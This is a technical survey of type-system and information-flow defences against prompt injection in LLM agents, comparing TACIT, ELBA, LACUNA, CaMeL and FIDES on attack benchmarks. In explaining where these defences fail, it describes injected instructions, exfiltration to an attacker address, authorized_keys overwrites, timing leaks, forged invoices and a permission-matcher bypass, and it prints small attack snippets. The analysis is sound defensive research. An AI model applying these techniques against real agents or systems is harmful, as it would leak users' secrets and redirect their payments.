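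This default matters because the newer version also lets a program post classified data to any permitted host. Judging by the README on Glama, if the operator sets no limit, a hijacked agent could name an attacker's server in its own request and send the budget there. The program would compile because the library allows classified data to leave the wrapper this way.

When a snippet prints the wrapped summary, the user's terminal shows the text, but the agent receives only `Classified(****)`. If the user then asks how long the summary is, the agent can print `summary.map(_.length)`, which shows the length to the user but not to the agent.

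A pure function can still throw an exception, and the message could contain the secret. Safe mode permits exceptions because almost any code can fail, for example by dividing by zero or running out of memory. TACIT catches them at runtime and turns them into ordinary values, which it can wrap. In the version for AgentDojo, the agent doesn't find out that a function on classified data failed. This hides even the one bit of information that a visible failure would reveal, but the agent may then believe a broken program worked while the user sees an empty result.

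### What a hijacked agent can still do

TACIT doesn't prevent hostile text from influencing the agent. A coding agent may read a comment in a source file as a plain string, treat it as an instruction and write its next snippet to follow it. The snippet still has to pass the compiler, but the attacker can do anything the agent's capabilities allow. For example, an injected comment could lead an agent with access to `/project` to delete the source code there, and that snippet would compile.

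Wrapping a file doesn't protect it from being overwritten either. According to the README on Glama, the mechanism protects "confidentiality, not integrity". A snippet can wrap any string with `classify` and write it to a classified file. If that file is `.ssh/authorized_keys`, which lists the keys accepted for login, an attacker might gain access to the whole machine. The operator can prevent this by making classified files read-only for the agent.

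Odersky and colleagues exclude timing and termination from the guarantee. A pure function can run indefinitely, so a malicious agent could write one that loops forever if the first bit of a secret is 1, then learn the bit from whether the snippet finishes. They mention the leak of a single bit, but the agent can submit another snippet to learn the next bit, much like a program in CaMeL's retry loop. The newer version's optional time limit wouldn't help, because the timeout error reveals the same bit.

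The guarantee also doesn't cover external programs, because the compiler never examines them. If the agent is allowed to run `python`, it can write a Python script to a file and run it without any of Scala's restrictions. Odersky and colleagues recommend permitting only specific commands, such as `git diff`, and adding a sandbox where security is critical.

### Trying to extract secrets from a project

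To test the protection, Odersky and colleagues set up a small Scala project with a folder of secrets, including API keys and internal documents. They wrote 10 prompt injections and 12 legitimate tasks, some of which needed the secrets, such as summarising a classified incident report. The simplest injections were instructions in code comments. Others imitated system messages, described the secrets as harmless test data or supplied finished Scala code for reading them.

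Pairing every task with every injection gives 120 trials. In 11 more, the user was the attacker and either asked for the secrets outright or pretended to be someone with authority, such as an administrator in an emergency. Each model ran all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets wrapped in `Classified` and once with them as plain strings. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

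| Model | Secrets | Leaks in 120 injection trials | Leaks in 11 malicious requests | Secure trials |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Wrapped | 0 | 0 | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Plain | 0 | 2 | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Wrapped | 0 | 0 | 100% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Plain | 3 | 8 | 91.6% |

Ten of the 13 leaks came from malicious users. Most of the other designs assume the user is honest, so they don't address this threat. The injections were weak. Sonnet resisted all 120 without relying on the types, so those trials show little about what the wrapper adds for that model.

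Most of these attacks try to persuade the model rather than exploit a compiler bug or use timing to extract a secret. If the type system works as intended, none of them can succeed, however persuasive, so the perfect score mainly confirms that the implementation has no obvious hole.

The wrapper didn't stop the agents from doing their work. With wrapped secrets, Sonnet gave a correct answer in 99.2% of the 120 injection trials and MiniMax in 90.0%. With plain strings, the figures were 83.3% and 88.3%. Odersky and colleagues suspect that their set-up caused the difference for Sonnet, because it often exceeded its time or turn limits and sometimes stopped to warn the user when it noticed an injection. The results therefore don't show that types make Sonnet better at these tasks.

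### TACIT on AgentDojo

Odersky and colleagues also moved AgentDojo's four environments to TACIT without changing the tasks or attacks. Emails, files, transactions, chat messages and reviews all come back wrapped. The agent can have a second model extract information from them inside `map`, and it can show the user a wrapped result, but it can't read the text. This is close to the dual-LLM pattern, with types enforcing the separation between the two models.

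In 1,926 attacked runs across two models, one attack counted as successful. The user had asked to book a particular hotel, and an injected review recommended a different one. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the review in its answer, and AgentDojo scores this attack as successful if the answer contains the other hotel's name. This doesn't seem to be a failure of the type system, since the user was allowed to see the reviews.

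The next table compares the percentage of tasks completed with the figures that CaMeL's designers had published for the same models.

| Environment | CaMeL, Gemini 2.5 Pro | TACIT, Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL, o4-mini | TACIT, o4-mini |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 52.8 | 56.9 | 62.5 | 59.0 |
| Workspace | 53.8 | 50.5 | 81.4 | 52.9 |
| Slack | 48.6 | 40.0 | 68.6 | 47.6 |
| Travel | 1.4 | 64.3 | 74.3 | 68.6 |

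Odersky and colleagues call TACIT and CaMeL comparable. That is reasonable for banking, but with o4-mini TACIT is about 29 percentage points behind CaMeL on workspace tasks and 21 behind on Slack. Some of the Slack gap may arise because even the list of channels comes back wrapped. CaMeL's 1.4% in travel with Gemini is so low that the cause is probably something other than its design.

In the banking version, the contents of a bill are wrapped, but `send_money`, called `sendMoney` in Scala, expects the recipient as a plain string. To pay the account number printed on a bill, the agent therefore has to call `sendMoney` inside `map`, which is supposed to accept only pure functions. The agent's instructions include a warning that side effects inside such functions run immediately, so this version apparently permits them. If so, the types prevent the agent from reading a malicious bill, but the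 attacker's account number can still reach the payment. The dual-LLM pattern has the same gap. None of the 288 banking attacks succeeded, but local purity can't be the reason if payments inside `map` are allowed.

### The cost of writing Scala

Models' training data contains little Scala with capture checking, so they might do worse writing it than calling tools directly. Odersky and colleagues tested this with ten runs per task on τ²-bench, which simulates customer service for an airline and a shop. Three models did slightly better when they wrote Scala. The gains ranged from 0.8 percentage points for DeepSeek V3.2 on airline tasks to 3.7 for gpt-oss-120b on shop tasks, where its score rose from 53.3% to 57.0%.

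Odersky and colleagues attribute the gains to structured results and helpful compiler errors. The Scala functions they list for these tasks, such as the one that cancels a reservation, have no capabilities in their signatures. The test therefore shows that models can work in Scala, but it gives little evidence about how well they work under tight capability restrictions.

SWE-bench Lite is a better test because the agent has to fix real software bugs and, with TACIT, all its file and shell operations go through capabilities. MiniMax M2.5 solved 41.7% of the 300 problems with TACIT and 43.3% with its usual tools, a difference of five problems. Coding agents rely heavily on shell commands, which TACIT makes more awkward to use.

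Compiler errors were rare on τ²-bench. Between 0.32% and 7.93% of snippets needed a retry, depending on the model and the type of task, and these took an average of 1.06 to 1.39 attempts. Common mistakes included mishandling missing values and forgetting that a dollar sign has a special meaning in some Scala strings. Compiling a snippet takes less than a second once the compiler is running. Capture checking accounts for only a small part of compile time, less than 15% for Scala's standard library according to *What's in the Box* (2025).

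### Whether taint marks survive a conversation

Odersky and colleagues argue that tracking taint at run time, as CaMeL does, has a structural gap because a value's "taint markers are lost" once it enters the model's conversation as ordinary text. TACIT avoids this problem by keeping classified text out of the agent's conversation.

The argument applies only to run-time tracking systems that label just the program's variables. FIDES and LLMbda also label the conversation, which preserves the labels, though only as one coarse label for the whole conversation.

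TACIT's better argument is that a label on the conversation can restrict what the agent does only after the company that hosts the model has received the text. That is too late if the company may be an adversary, as TACIT assumes. An LLMbda program could check each message before sending it, but a developer would have to add that check, whereas TACIT withholds classified text by default. As a result, TACIT's agent can't choose its next step based on a classified document. A FIDES planner can read the document, but it gives up some permissions by doing so.

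TACIT doesn't keep track of which text is untrusted. Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, describe it as enforcing "a limited form of IFC". `Classified` records that a value is secret, but not who wrote it or who may read it. If a web page comes back as a plain string, it enters the conversation without a label, and the agent's next snippet has the same permissions as before. In the same situation, FIDES could block a later payment or email. A developer can wrap web pages in `Classified`, as in the AgentDojo version, but then the agent can't read them.

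## LBAC and LACUNA, which check agent code against the surrounding program

TACIT's compiler checks the snippets an agent writes, but not the program around the agent. If the developer's code writes the agent's answer to a public file, TACIT doesn't check that step. In language-based agent control (LBAC), which Zhou and colleagues introduced in May 2026, the developer and the agent write in the same typed language. The agent's code has to type-check at the point in the developer's program that uses its result, so one policy can cover both.

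### A model call with a type

Zhou and colleagues built LBAC in Haskell. They first called the implementation TypeGuard and have since renamed it ELBA. It adds one function to the language:

```
agent :: Defs -> Prompt -> t
```

`Defs` lists the functions and types the agent may use, `Prompt` describes the task, and `t` is whatever type the surrounding program needs. When a run reaches the call, ELBA sends all three to a model, which replies with a Haskell expression. If the expression has type `t`, ELBA runs it. Otherwise, the model gets the error and tries again.

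Haskell is a pure language, so an expression's type shows which effects it can have. Code that reads a file or runs a shell command has a type marked `IO`. Suppose a developer offers a public calculator by calling `agent` with the expected type `Int`, and a user asks it to delete all files on the server and then compute a factorial. If the model writes that program, the deletion gives it an `IO` type instead of `Int`, so ELBA rejects it.

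Most agents need some effects, so the developer defines a narrower effect type that permits only a few operations. Any code of that type, whoever wrote it, is limited to those operations. The outermost layer of the application still has type `IO` because it has to start the restricted part. The policy doesn't cover that layer, so the developer has to make sure it is correct.

A call to `agent` sends its prompt to a model, but the call's type doesn't show this and can be simply `Int`. If another company hosts the model, that company receives any confidential text in the prompt, a leak that TACIT was designed to prevent.

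### Files, citations and labels

The first of the three case studies restricts file access. Agent code has the type `RIO` and can open a file only with a `Path`, an object capability for one folder and its contents. The call `readRIO "/etc/passwd"` doesn't compile, because a string isn't a `Path`. The agent can narrow a path with the operator `//`, so this does compile:

```
readRIO (root // "../../etc/passwd")
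```

The library, not the compiler, resolves the path string. It does so at runtime, following any symbolic links, and stops the program if the result lies outside `root`. Zhou and colleagues contrast this with permission rules that match the text of shell commands. In March 2026, a bug in Claude Code let forbidden commands through when they followed `&&`, because the matcher checked only the first part of the line.

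In the second case study, an agent compiles bibliographies, and every entry must come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The function that fetches an entry returns a `Trusted Bib`, and the function that writes to the file accepts only that type. Agent code can sort and filter these values but can't create or edit one, because the library hides the constructor. The types enforce nearly all of the DBLP requirement, and no label or path needs checking during the run.

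Across 100 tasks, the ELBA agent wrote 925 citations, none with a wrong author, year or DOI (the paper's permanent identifier). An ordinary agent with web search got 19 of 1,002 wrong. The types don't ensure that a cited paper is relevant to the topic.

The third case study uses information-flow control and leaves much more of the checking to run time. It relies on LIO, a Haskell library that Stefan, Russo and colleagues (2012) describe in *Flexible Dynamic Information Flow Control in the Presence of Exceptions*. They chose run-time labels because static analysis works poorly when new users and kinds of data appear while a program is running, as they constantly do for an agent.

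LIO keeps a current label for the whole computation, much as FIDES does for its context, and checks it before each write. This program, adapted from one in the LBAC paper, compiles:

```
forward :: DC ()
forward = do
  page <- httpGet "http://example.com/news"
  sendToManager page
```

`DC` is the type of LIO computations with this kind of label. After the first step, the label records that example.com has influenced the computation. If `sendToManager` requires trusted data, LIO stops the program there. The type guarantees only that agent code can't avoid these checks. Ordinary `IO` operations don't type-check in a `DC` program, and the constructor that would convert them is private to the library.

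LIO can also set a clearance, an upper limit on the current label. A program can't read a secret above its clearance. Like LLMbda, though, LIO doesn't prevent a program that can read a secret from revealing it by running forever.

ELBA retries only after type errors. A type error stops the program before it has done anything, so ELBA can safely request another version. A label error can occur halfway through, after the program has sent one message and before it sends the next.

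### How subagents inherit limits

ELBA's `agent` function generates a whole program at once, with no loop that feeds results back to the model. But the generated program can call `agent` again and include its results in the new prompt. For example, a bibliography agent can run one search, inspect the first result, and then have a subagent decide whether to refine the search.

Haskell infers the subagent's type from the code around the call. In a program of type `BibIO`, which covers bibliography effects, a subagent that acts as the next step must also have type `BibIO`, so it can do nothing its parent couldn't. The parent can give the subagent a stricter type, such as a plain `String` with no effects, but giving it type `IO` stops the parent's program from compiling. In the LIO version, a subagent that acts within its parent's computation also starts with the parent's current label, so a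 parent that has read an untrusted page can't regain its permissions by delegating.

LIO's `toLabeled` function keeps a computation's taint from spreading to its caller. It runs the computation separately and returns the result sealed with a label, without raising the caller's label. A subagent inside `toLabeled` resembles the quarantined model in the dual-LLM pattern, except that it can still use tools, subject to label checks. For example, it can open a web page mentioned in an untrusted message and draft a summary, which the parent sends without reading. The sending function checks that the parent's label is still trusted, so the page can't have influenced the choice of recipient.

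Zhou and colleagues prove that if a type in the host language guarantees some property of a program's tool calls, the property still holds when programs of that type contain `agent` calls. The proof replaces each `agent` call that may nest to depth n with an ordinary function that queries the model, type-checks the reply and runs it. Calls inside the reply have a smaller depth, so the proof has already dealt with them, and at depth 0 the function returns nothing. The result is an ordinary program with the same tool calls, so the original guarantee applies to it.

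The theorem carries over the guarantees that the language and its libraries actually enforce, so a bug in the path check would carry over too. It also needs Safe Haskell, a subset of Haskell without the functions that hide effects. Garby and colleagues point out that LBAC, like TACIT, has no machine-checked theorem about the complete agent system.

Inheritance limits a subagent to its parent's permissions, but a hijacked parent can pass on all of them, so the developer has to impose any tighter limit. *Authority Is Not a String* (2026) describes CapScope, which imposes tighter limits on coding agents at run time. It fixes the maximum permissions for a task before reading the repository, then gives each subagent its own smaller set. For example, the subagent that runs the code can't write to the file that another subagent patches.

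### ELBA on AgentDojo's Slack tasks

In the May version of the tests, as Garby and colleagues report them, TypeGuard completed 15 of the 21 Slack tasks without policies and 8 with them, against 7 for CaMeL with policies. It resisted all 105 pairs of a task and an injection. Zhou and colleagues have since redone the tests with four newer models. The table shows how many of the 21 tasks each system completed when nobody attacked:

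| System | Opus 4.7 | Opus 4.8 | GPT 5.4 | Sonnet 5 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| ELBA, policies on | 10 | 9 | 10 | 8 |
| CaMeL, policies on | 5 | 6 | 5 | 4 |
| ELBA, policies off | 18 | 16 | 16 | 14 |
| CaMeL, policies off | 15 | 16 | 17 | 13 |

With policies on, ELBA completes nearly twice as many tasks as CaMeL, and it keeps that lead across the 105 comparable pairs of attacked runs. With policies off, the two complete similar numbers of tasks. ELBA takes about three times as long because its agents query the model again as data comes in. The models had little trouble writing Haskell. They needed an average of 0.13 retries per run, and only 7 of 2,688 runs used all their permitted retries.

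The attack results changed more than the completion rates. Garby and colleagues had argued that TypeGuard's perfect score came entirely from its types, since its agents mix reading and acting. In the newer tests, both systems resisted all 105 injections even with policies off, because the models ignored AgentDojo's attacks. The score therefore gives almost no evidence about the types.

Zhou and colleagues therefore simulated a model that always obeys injections. Whenever a subagent received data containing an injection, ELBA replaced the subagent's task with the attacker's text. They ran this seven times for each model, giving 735 attacked runs per model. Without policies, Opus 4.7 resisted 425, Opus 4.8 resisted 460 and Sonnet 5 resisted 540. For GPT 5.4, the paper gives 670 in one table and 84.5%, or about 621, in another. With policies, all four resisted every attack, after the researchers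 had read and dismissed fewer than 30 runs in which the agent had only opened a harmless fixed web address. This is much better evidence for the policies than the ordinary benchmark, although the injections still came from AgentDojo and were not designed to get around labels.

ELBA completes 6 to 8 fewer of the 21 tasks when policies are enforced. According to Garby and colleagues, the May version of the paper explained such losses by saying that many tasks "involve flows that no secure policy would admit". This explanation has some support, since the Slack tasks often have the agent act on what a message or web page says, and FIDES, with different policies, also completed only about half of them. But if the tasks alone caused the losses, ELBA and CaMeL should lose roughly the same number, and with Opus 4.7 CaMeL completes half as many as ELBA. Whether a flow is secure also depends on whom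 the user trusts. A user who wants the agent to follow a colleague's message can endorse it, which makes the flow acceptable under the same rules. The current version says more cautiously that policies may also rule out legitimate behaviour.

### LACUNA's typed holes

LACUNA, also from May 2026, applies a similar idea to Scala using typed holes, which are gaps in a program whose expected type the compiler knows. *Statically Contextualizing Large Language Models with Typed Holes* (Blinn, Li and colleagues, 2024) combined such holes with language models to help programmers while they edit code. In LACUNA, the hole stays in the finished program, and a model fills it each time execution reaches it.

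Suppose the office assistant contains this function:

```
def cancelFriday(calendar: Calendar, mail: Mailer, team: String): Receipt =
  agent[Receipt]("Cancel Friday's meeting and tell the team")
```

The hole is the call to `agent`. The code that fills it may use `calendar`, `mail`, `team` and anything else in scope, and it has to produce a `Receipt`, which is what `mail.send` returns. The model writes:

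```
calendar.cancel("Friday")
mail.send(team, reason)
```

The variable `reason` doesn't exist, so a Python agent would probably cancel the meeting and then crash on the second line without notifying the team. LACUNA inserts the two lines into the text of the surrounding function and runs the Scala compiler on the result. The compiler reports the unknown name, so neither line runs and the meeting stays in the calendar. The model gets the error message and replaces `reason` with its own sentence, and this version compiles and runs.

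The developer of an ELBA agent lists the functions the agent may use, whereas a LACUNA hole gets everything in scope. This is convenient, but it can give the model more than the task needs. To limit this, a developer can put the hole in a separate function and pass in only the necessary values. Ordinary Scala types also don't record effects as Haskell's do, so the stronger limits depend on capture checking, which is optional in LACUNA, and on the safe mode that TACIT uses.

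With those switched on, LACUNA removes one of TACIT's restrictions. TACIT's agent has to write the function for a classified document before anyone has read it. In LACUNA, that function can contain a hole, which a trusted local model fills after reading the document. The new code must still be pure, so it can't send the text anywhere.

### What LACUNA's tests found

LACUNA tested its compiler on its own set of about 400 cases, each combining a host program with a good or bad snippet, and the compiler handled all of them correctly. It also tested the full system on BrowseComp-Plus, a set of 830 hard research questions over a fixed collection of documents. With DeepSeek V4 Flash, the system answered 27.1% correctly. The compiler rejected 8.6% of the generated snippets, and a question needed 0.7 retries on average. The test compared different models in LACUNA but didn't include agents without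 type-checking, so it can't show any loss in performance from the checking.

The customer service tasks in τ²-bench do allow a comparison between LACUNA and ordinary tool calls. DeepSeek solved 76.0% of 392 tasks with LACUNA and 90.0% with tool calls. The LACUNA paper describes these results as on par, but a gap of 14 percentage points is large, and the gap on the shop tasks was 22 points. The smaller Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite solved 29.1% with LACUNA and 33.2% without it. On one group of tasks, the compiler rejected 89% of the code that Gemini wrote, so that code did no harm but also did nothing for the customer.

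On AgentDojo, LACUNA completed slightly more tasks than TACIT in seven of eight comparisons, each covering one environment and one model. It also let through more attacks, 8 of 1,898, compared with 1 for TACIT. With either system, a hijacked model can still misuse any capability the task needs.

### The wrong recipient

The function that cancels Friday's meeting has this weakness. If an injected instruction gets into the prompt, the model might write:

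```
mail.send("someone@attacker.com", "Friday's meeting is cancelled")
```

The code compiles because the address is a string and the result is a `Receipt`. A developer can rule out every address outside the company by defining a type `Colleague`, whose values come only from the company directory, and having `mail.send` accept only that type. `Trusted Bib` works the same way. LACUNA also suggests adding conditions to types, such as requiring a number to stay below some limit, which could cap the size of a payment.

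The model can still choose the wrong colleague. If an untrusted message influenced the choice, a label check like the one in LIO can catch this during the run. But if the user asked for Bob in accounting and the model picked Bob in sales from the same trusted directory, both the type check and the label check pass, and the message goes to Bob in sales.

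## What attack benchmarks show about the guarantees

LLMbda's noninterference theorem covers every run of every program in the language, including runs under attacks nobody has thought of yet, as long as its assumptions hold, while a benchmark covers only the attacks it includes. But a benchmark also tests parts of the system that are assumed correct in the theorem, such as the labels on the data and the checks inside the tools, so it can expose mistakes in them. It also measures how many tasks the agent completes.

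Most papers on designs that enforce labels or types report few or no successful attacks on AgentDojo. These results are weaker evidence that the enforcement works if something else could have stopped the attacks.

### Attacks that never reach the checks

Garby and colleagues count 97 of AgentDojo's 144 banking pairs in which planning before reading should defeat the attack even without label checks, so only the other 47 pairs test those checks.

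A single success rate mixes the two groups. Suppose an agent of this kind has faulty label checks that let through the attacks in 24 of the 47 pairs. It would still resist the attacks in 120 of the 144 pairs, or 83%. With no checks and a model that follows every injected instruction, it would resist 67%.

Even the 47 pairs test the checks only when the attack would otherwise have worked. With its policies switched off, CaMeL still resisted the attack in all 141 runs on these pairs with GPT-5.2 and in 138 of 141 with MiMo-v2.5, presumably because the models ignored most of the injected text. The policies therefore had to stop very few attacks for CaMeL to get its perfect score with them on.

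The 97 easy pairs are not easy for TACIT and ELBA, because their models can write more code after receiving results, and that code could include a payment the user never asked for. Garby and colleagues conclude that, for these two systems, every pair in effect tests the type system.

To test TACIT, Odersky and colleagues used their own version of AgentDojo, in which the emails, files and transactions are wrapped so that an injected command normally never enters the agent's conversation. The types still provide the protection, but they do so by hiding the command, so the runs provide little evidence about what happens once an agent has been fooled.

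The better evidence for ELBA comes from Zhou and colleagues' simulated model that always obeys injections. Other teams could usefully copy this simulation, since far more of the attacks reach the checks.

### What a perfect score supports

With two of its three models, Randori resisted all 141 runs on the 47 harder pairs. These were three repetitions of each pair, and repetitions tend to turn out alike. With GPT-5.2, for instance, both failures came from the same pair. Garby and colleagues therefore treat the sample as 47 pairs, not 141 runs, and calculate a Wilson score interval, a standard way to put a range around a proportion. When all n trials succeed, the lower end of the interval is

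n / (n + z²),

where z is 1.96 for 95% confidence. For 47 pairs this gives 47 / (47 + 3.84) = 92.4%.

A direct calculation gives almost the same result. If an agent's true resistance rate were 92.4%, its chance of resisting 47 independent attacks in a row would be 0.924⁴⁷, or about 2.4%. A lower true rate would make a perfect score even less likely. Treating the 141 runs as independent would raise the lower end of the interval to 97.3%, even though the additional runs only repeat the same 47 attacks.

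The perfect score is compatible with about one attack in 13 succeeding. An agent would need a perfect score on 381 pairs to support a resistance rate of 99%, and on about 3,840 to support 99.9%. The original AgentDojo has 629 pairs, and many of them don't test the enforcement in a system that plans first.

The interval also holds only if future attacks resemble a random draw from the benchmark, but a real attacker would pick one that works, such as the forged bill that beat Randori. A theorem, by contrast, covers the attacks an attacker would pick as well as the typical ones.

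### Attacks that AgentDojo misjudged

One of the planners that Costa and colleagues tested stores untrusted tool results in variables it can never read, so injected text doesn't reach its model. AgentDojo still counted 12 successful attacks against it, all in the travel tasks. Costa and colleagues read through the attacks that AgentDojo had scored as successful and judged that none of these 12 was a real injection.

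Some of the errors are bugs in AgentDojo's scoring. One Slack attack tries to get an outsider invited to the workspace, and AgentDojo checks only whether the agent called the invitation tool, so it counts the attack as a success even if the policy blocked the call. Other attacks only change the wording of an answer.

The case for excluding a third group is weaker. One travel attack makes the agent create a calendar event with no participants. Costa and colleagues don't count it because their policy allows such events, which they say leak nothing. But the user never asked for the event. If researchers exclude whatever the policy allows, a system that enforces its policy correctly will always score zero. The corrected score of zero for FIDES is good evidence that the enforcement works, but it doesn't show that the policy is strict enough.

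AgentDojo also scores some user tasks incorrectly. The planner that can't open its variables got credit for recommending a highly rated hotel without seeing any ratings, and for finding the price of a New Year's gift by picking the only transaction dated 1 January. In a few tasks the right response is to stop because information is missing, and a planner that can't read anything does that by default. Small differences in completion rates between systems may partly reflect such luck.

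### Where the labels came from

AgentDojo has no labels for which data is trustworthy, so each team has to add its own. To get a clear baseline, Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks targets it. They could instead have used facts that a real system can check. For example, mail servers can authenticate a sender's address, and outsiders can't tamper with some system-generated timestamps.

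A real deployment can't do this, because it has no list of the fields attackers will use. No attack in the test could arrive through a field that somebody had forgotten to label, which is one of the likelier ways for such a system to fail in practice.

Treating fields that no attack targets as trusted may also overstate the agent's usefulness, because those fields stay visible to the planner. For example, transaction amounts counted as trusted, although anyone who sends the user money chooses the amount. FIDES relied on such a field when it changed a password because of one large transaction. With stricter labels, the agent would probably have completed fewer tasks.

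*Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) argues that every labelling scheme depends on this first assignment of labels, and that researchers have left it under-specified.

### A forged bill and a quoted review

Two cases recur among the remaining attacks. One is the forged bill in a file that the user had told the agent to obey. It beat Randori and is one of only two successful attacks that CaMeL's designers reported against their own system. The other is the hostile hotel review that the agent quotes word for word in its answer. It accounts for CaMeL's other failure, TACIT's only failure, and some of the cases that Costa and colleagues discounted. Garby and colleagues think the same attacks remain across four independent systems because of a limit of information-flow methods, not a weakness in any one design.

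This seems right for the bill, because the genuine and forged versions come from the same file and so carry the same label. More careful tracking wouldn't help, but finer labels might, for instance if the system recorded who last edited the file or if suppliers signed their bills.

The review looks more like a flaw in the test, since the user was allowed to read it. A better test would check whether the agent recommends the attacker's hotel as its own opinion, which could mislead someone.

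*Beyond Instruction Override* (Zhang, Bertran and colleagues, 2026) classifies planted text as prompt injection when it tries to influence a decision that its source has no authority to make. A false claim about a matter within its source's authority is misinformation, and detecting it usually takes independent evidence. By this definition, a forged bill in a file is misinformation if the user has told the agent to pay what the file says. CaMeL's designers therefore have a reasonable argument for putting this case outside their threat model, although the user still loses the money.

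### Attackers who adapt

AgentDojo's standard attacks have fixed wording, and *Architecting Secure AI Agents* (2026) describes nearly all benchmark attacks as static and simple. Fixed attacks greatly overstated the security of defences that filter text or train a model to ignore injections. Narisetty and colleagues report that Nasr and colleagues attacked twelve such defences with full knowledge of how each worked. In the original evaluations, attack success was close to zero for most of the defences, but the new attacks had success rates above 90% against most of them. That study did not include system-level defences, which restrict what the agent can do instead of trying to recognise malicious text.

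*AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested both kinds with an attacker that adapts to the results of earlier attempts. A separate model receives a list of earlier injections with the number of times each one worked, proposes an explanation for the results, and writes a new injection. It gets six attempts per target. It isn't told which defence is in place, and its only feedback is the success counts.

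The rewritten attacks got past PIGuard, a classifier that removes suspicious sentences. On GPT-4o-mini, they succeeded against it in 28.0% of pairs, while the fixed attack never did. One of the rewritten attacks, which the automated search found on its own, is a forged invoice with a notice that the payment details have changed. No sentence in it reads like a command, so PIGuard lets it through and the agent pays the attacker.

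CaMeL held up much better. The table covers 389 pairs from the banking, Slack and travel tasks, and all figures are percentages.

| Model | Adaptive attacks that succeed, no defence | Adaptive attacks that succeed, CaMeL | Tasks completed, no defence | Tasks completed, CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o-mini | 52.4 | 0.0 | 66.7 | 26.3 |
| GPT-5.4-mini | 8.7 | 1.8 | 77.2 | 52.6 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 34.7 | 0.3 | 63.2 | 28.1 |
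| DeepSeek-v4-Flash | 16.5 | 0.5 | 89.5 | 38.6 |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 1.8 | 0.5 | 70.2 | 40.4 |

Rewriting the attacks made almost no difference to CaMeL's results. This is expected, because CaMeL tracks where each value came from, and rewording an attack doesn't change that. All of CaMeL's failures were in the travel tasks, so quoted reviews may account for some of them.

The protection lowers the task completion rate by 25 to 51 percentage points. With Claude Haiku 4.5, CaMeL prevented about five of the 389 attacks and lowered the completion rate by 30 points. That looks like a poor trade, although a stronger attacker might find more ways to fool the unprotected model.

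This attacker can only reword its text. It has no access to CaMeL's code, so it can't look for a flaw such as the leak through a skipped branch, and it can learn very little from the success counts when every attempt fails. The results are therefore good evidence that rewording doesn't defeat CaMeL's labels, but little evidence of how CaMeL would hold up against an attacker who studies the interpreter and the policies.

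Narisetty and colleagues call for tests by attackers who know the defence, and ran a small one on Progent. Progent checks each tool call against rules that a model writes from the user's request. On Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, it cut the success rate of ordinary attacks from 25.8% to 4.2%. An attack designed specifically for Progent succeeded in 2.6% of cases. That attack used a single handwritten template, which may have been weak, since it did no better than the ordinary attacks. Narisetty and colleagues present the result as one small data point.

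### Attacks that change a value in the user's own task

In November 2026, Zhang and colleagues published a benchmark that leaves out the easy attacks that an agent can defeat by planning first. In each of its 90 cases, the attacker tampers with the task the agent is already doing. For example, a user asks the agent to settle a dispute over a damaged item and to base the refund on the platform's order record, which authorises $899.99. The buyer's evidence includes a claim that the refund should be $1,074.99. The agent has to issue a refund anyway, so the attacker only has to change the amount.

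Limiting which tools an agent may call did little to stop attacks here. Across five models, attacks succeeded in 17.0% of runs without a defence and 15.4% with Progent. In a closer analysis of two of the models, the agents attempted 116 calls that the attacker wanted, and Progent blocked eight. The other 108 used a permitted tool with arguments that Progent's rules accepted.

With CaMeL, 1.3% of attacks succeeded, and the wording again made little difference. Each case comes in up to six versions, from a direct command to refund $1,074.99 to a false statement that this is the authorised total, and CaMeL's rate stayed between 1.0% and 1.5% for every version. The DRIFT system's filter, which removes injected instructions, cut the success rate of direct commands to 2.4%, but false statements about the current situation still succeeded 12.1% of the time.

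However, CaMeL completed only 13.3% of the tasks when nobody attacked, compared with 95.3% for agents without a defence. An agent that fails to issue any refunds also issues no wrong ones, so the 1.3% reflects both attacks that CaMeL stopped and tasks that it never carried out. Some of the loss may be due to the policies and labels, which Zhang and colleagues had to write themselves for the new environments. According to Ma and colleagues, AgentDyn, another 2026 benchmark with more open-ended tasks, recorded no successful attacks against CaMeL but also no completed tasks with any model tested.

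Zhang and colleagues suggest accepting each important argument only from a source with the authority to set it. In the refund case, that source is the order record, and a label check could enforce the rule because the record and the buyer's evidence have different origins. But the next dispute may depend on a delivery date or a test result, and somebody would have to specify which source has the authority to set it.

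## Which checks must wait until the agent runs

Before the agent handles any dispute, a developer can write the rule that a refund must match the order record, but nobody can apply the rule until there is an amount to compare. Many security rules for agents can likewise be written early but applied only later, because a check can't happen until the facts it needs are available.

### The office assistant at four moments

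Suppose the office assistant has only its two email tools and uses a planner like CaMeL's. The user asks for the Project X summary again, but this time tells the assistant to find the manager's address in the emails. More facts become available as the work proceeds:

1. When the developer builds the assistant, an analyser can establish that no run shares a file or creates a calendar event.
2. When the planner writes its program, an analyser can establish that the program sends one email and takes the recipient from the emails. It can't determine the address.
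3. When the program calls `send_email`, the address is an actual string, and the interpreter has the labels of the emails it came from. Code can now compare the address with the company directory and check whether that person may read the summary.
4. After the call, the mail server normally confirms that it accepted the message. If the connection drops first, the assistant can't tell whether the manager will get the summary.

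An ordinary agent loop has no plan, so the checks that CaMeLoT makes at the second moment must wait until each call. TACIT can make some of these checks earlier, because its compiler examines each snippet before it runs.

Three run-time designs don't depend on a particular planner or programming language. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) checks each call against rules about tool names and arguments. *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) describes CXI, which checks whether each part of a call comes from a source with the authority to set it. *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) describes a runtime for agents that add tools and keep memory. The table arranges these and the earlier systems by when they can act.

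| What the check has to establish | Earliest moment | A system that checks it |
|---|---|---|
| The loop has a hard limit on steps | Software built | IAL-Scan |
| A plan makes only permitted calls in a permitted order | Plan written | CaMeLoT |
| A snippet holds the permission it uses | Snippet written | TACIT's compiler |
| The actual recipient or amount is allowed | Tool called | Progent |
| The actual path is inside the permitted folder | Tool called | TACIT's library |
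| Returned data has a trusted source | Result returned | FIDES |
| A value up for endorsement is on a fixed list | Result returned | LLMbda, with a wrapper |
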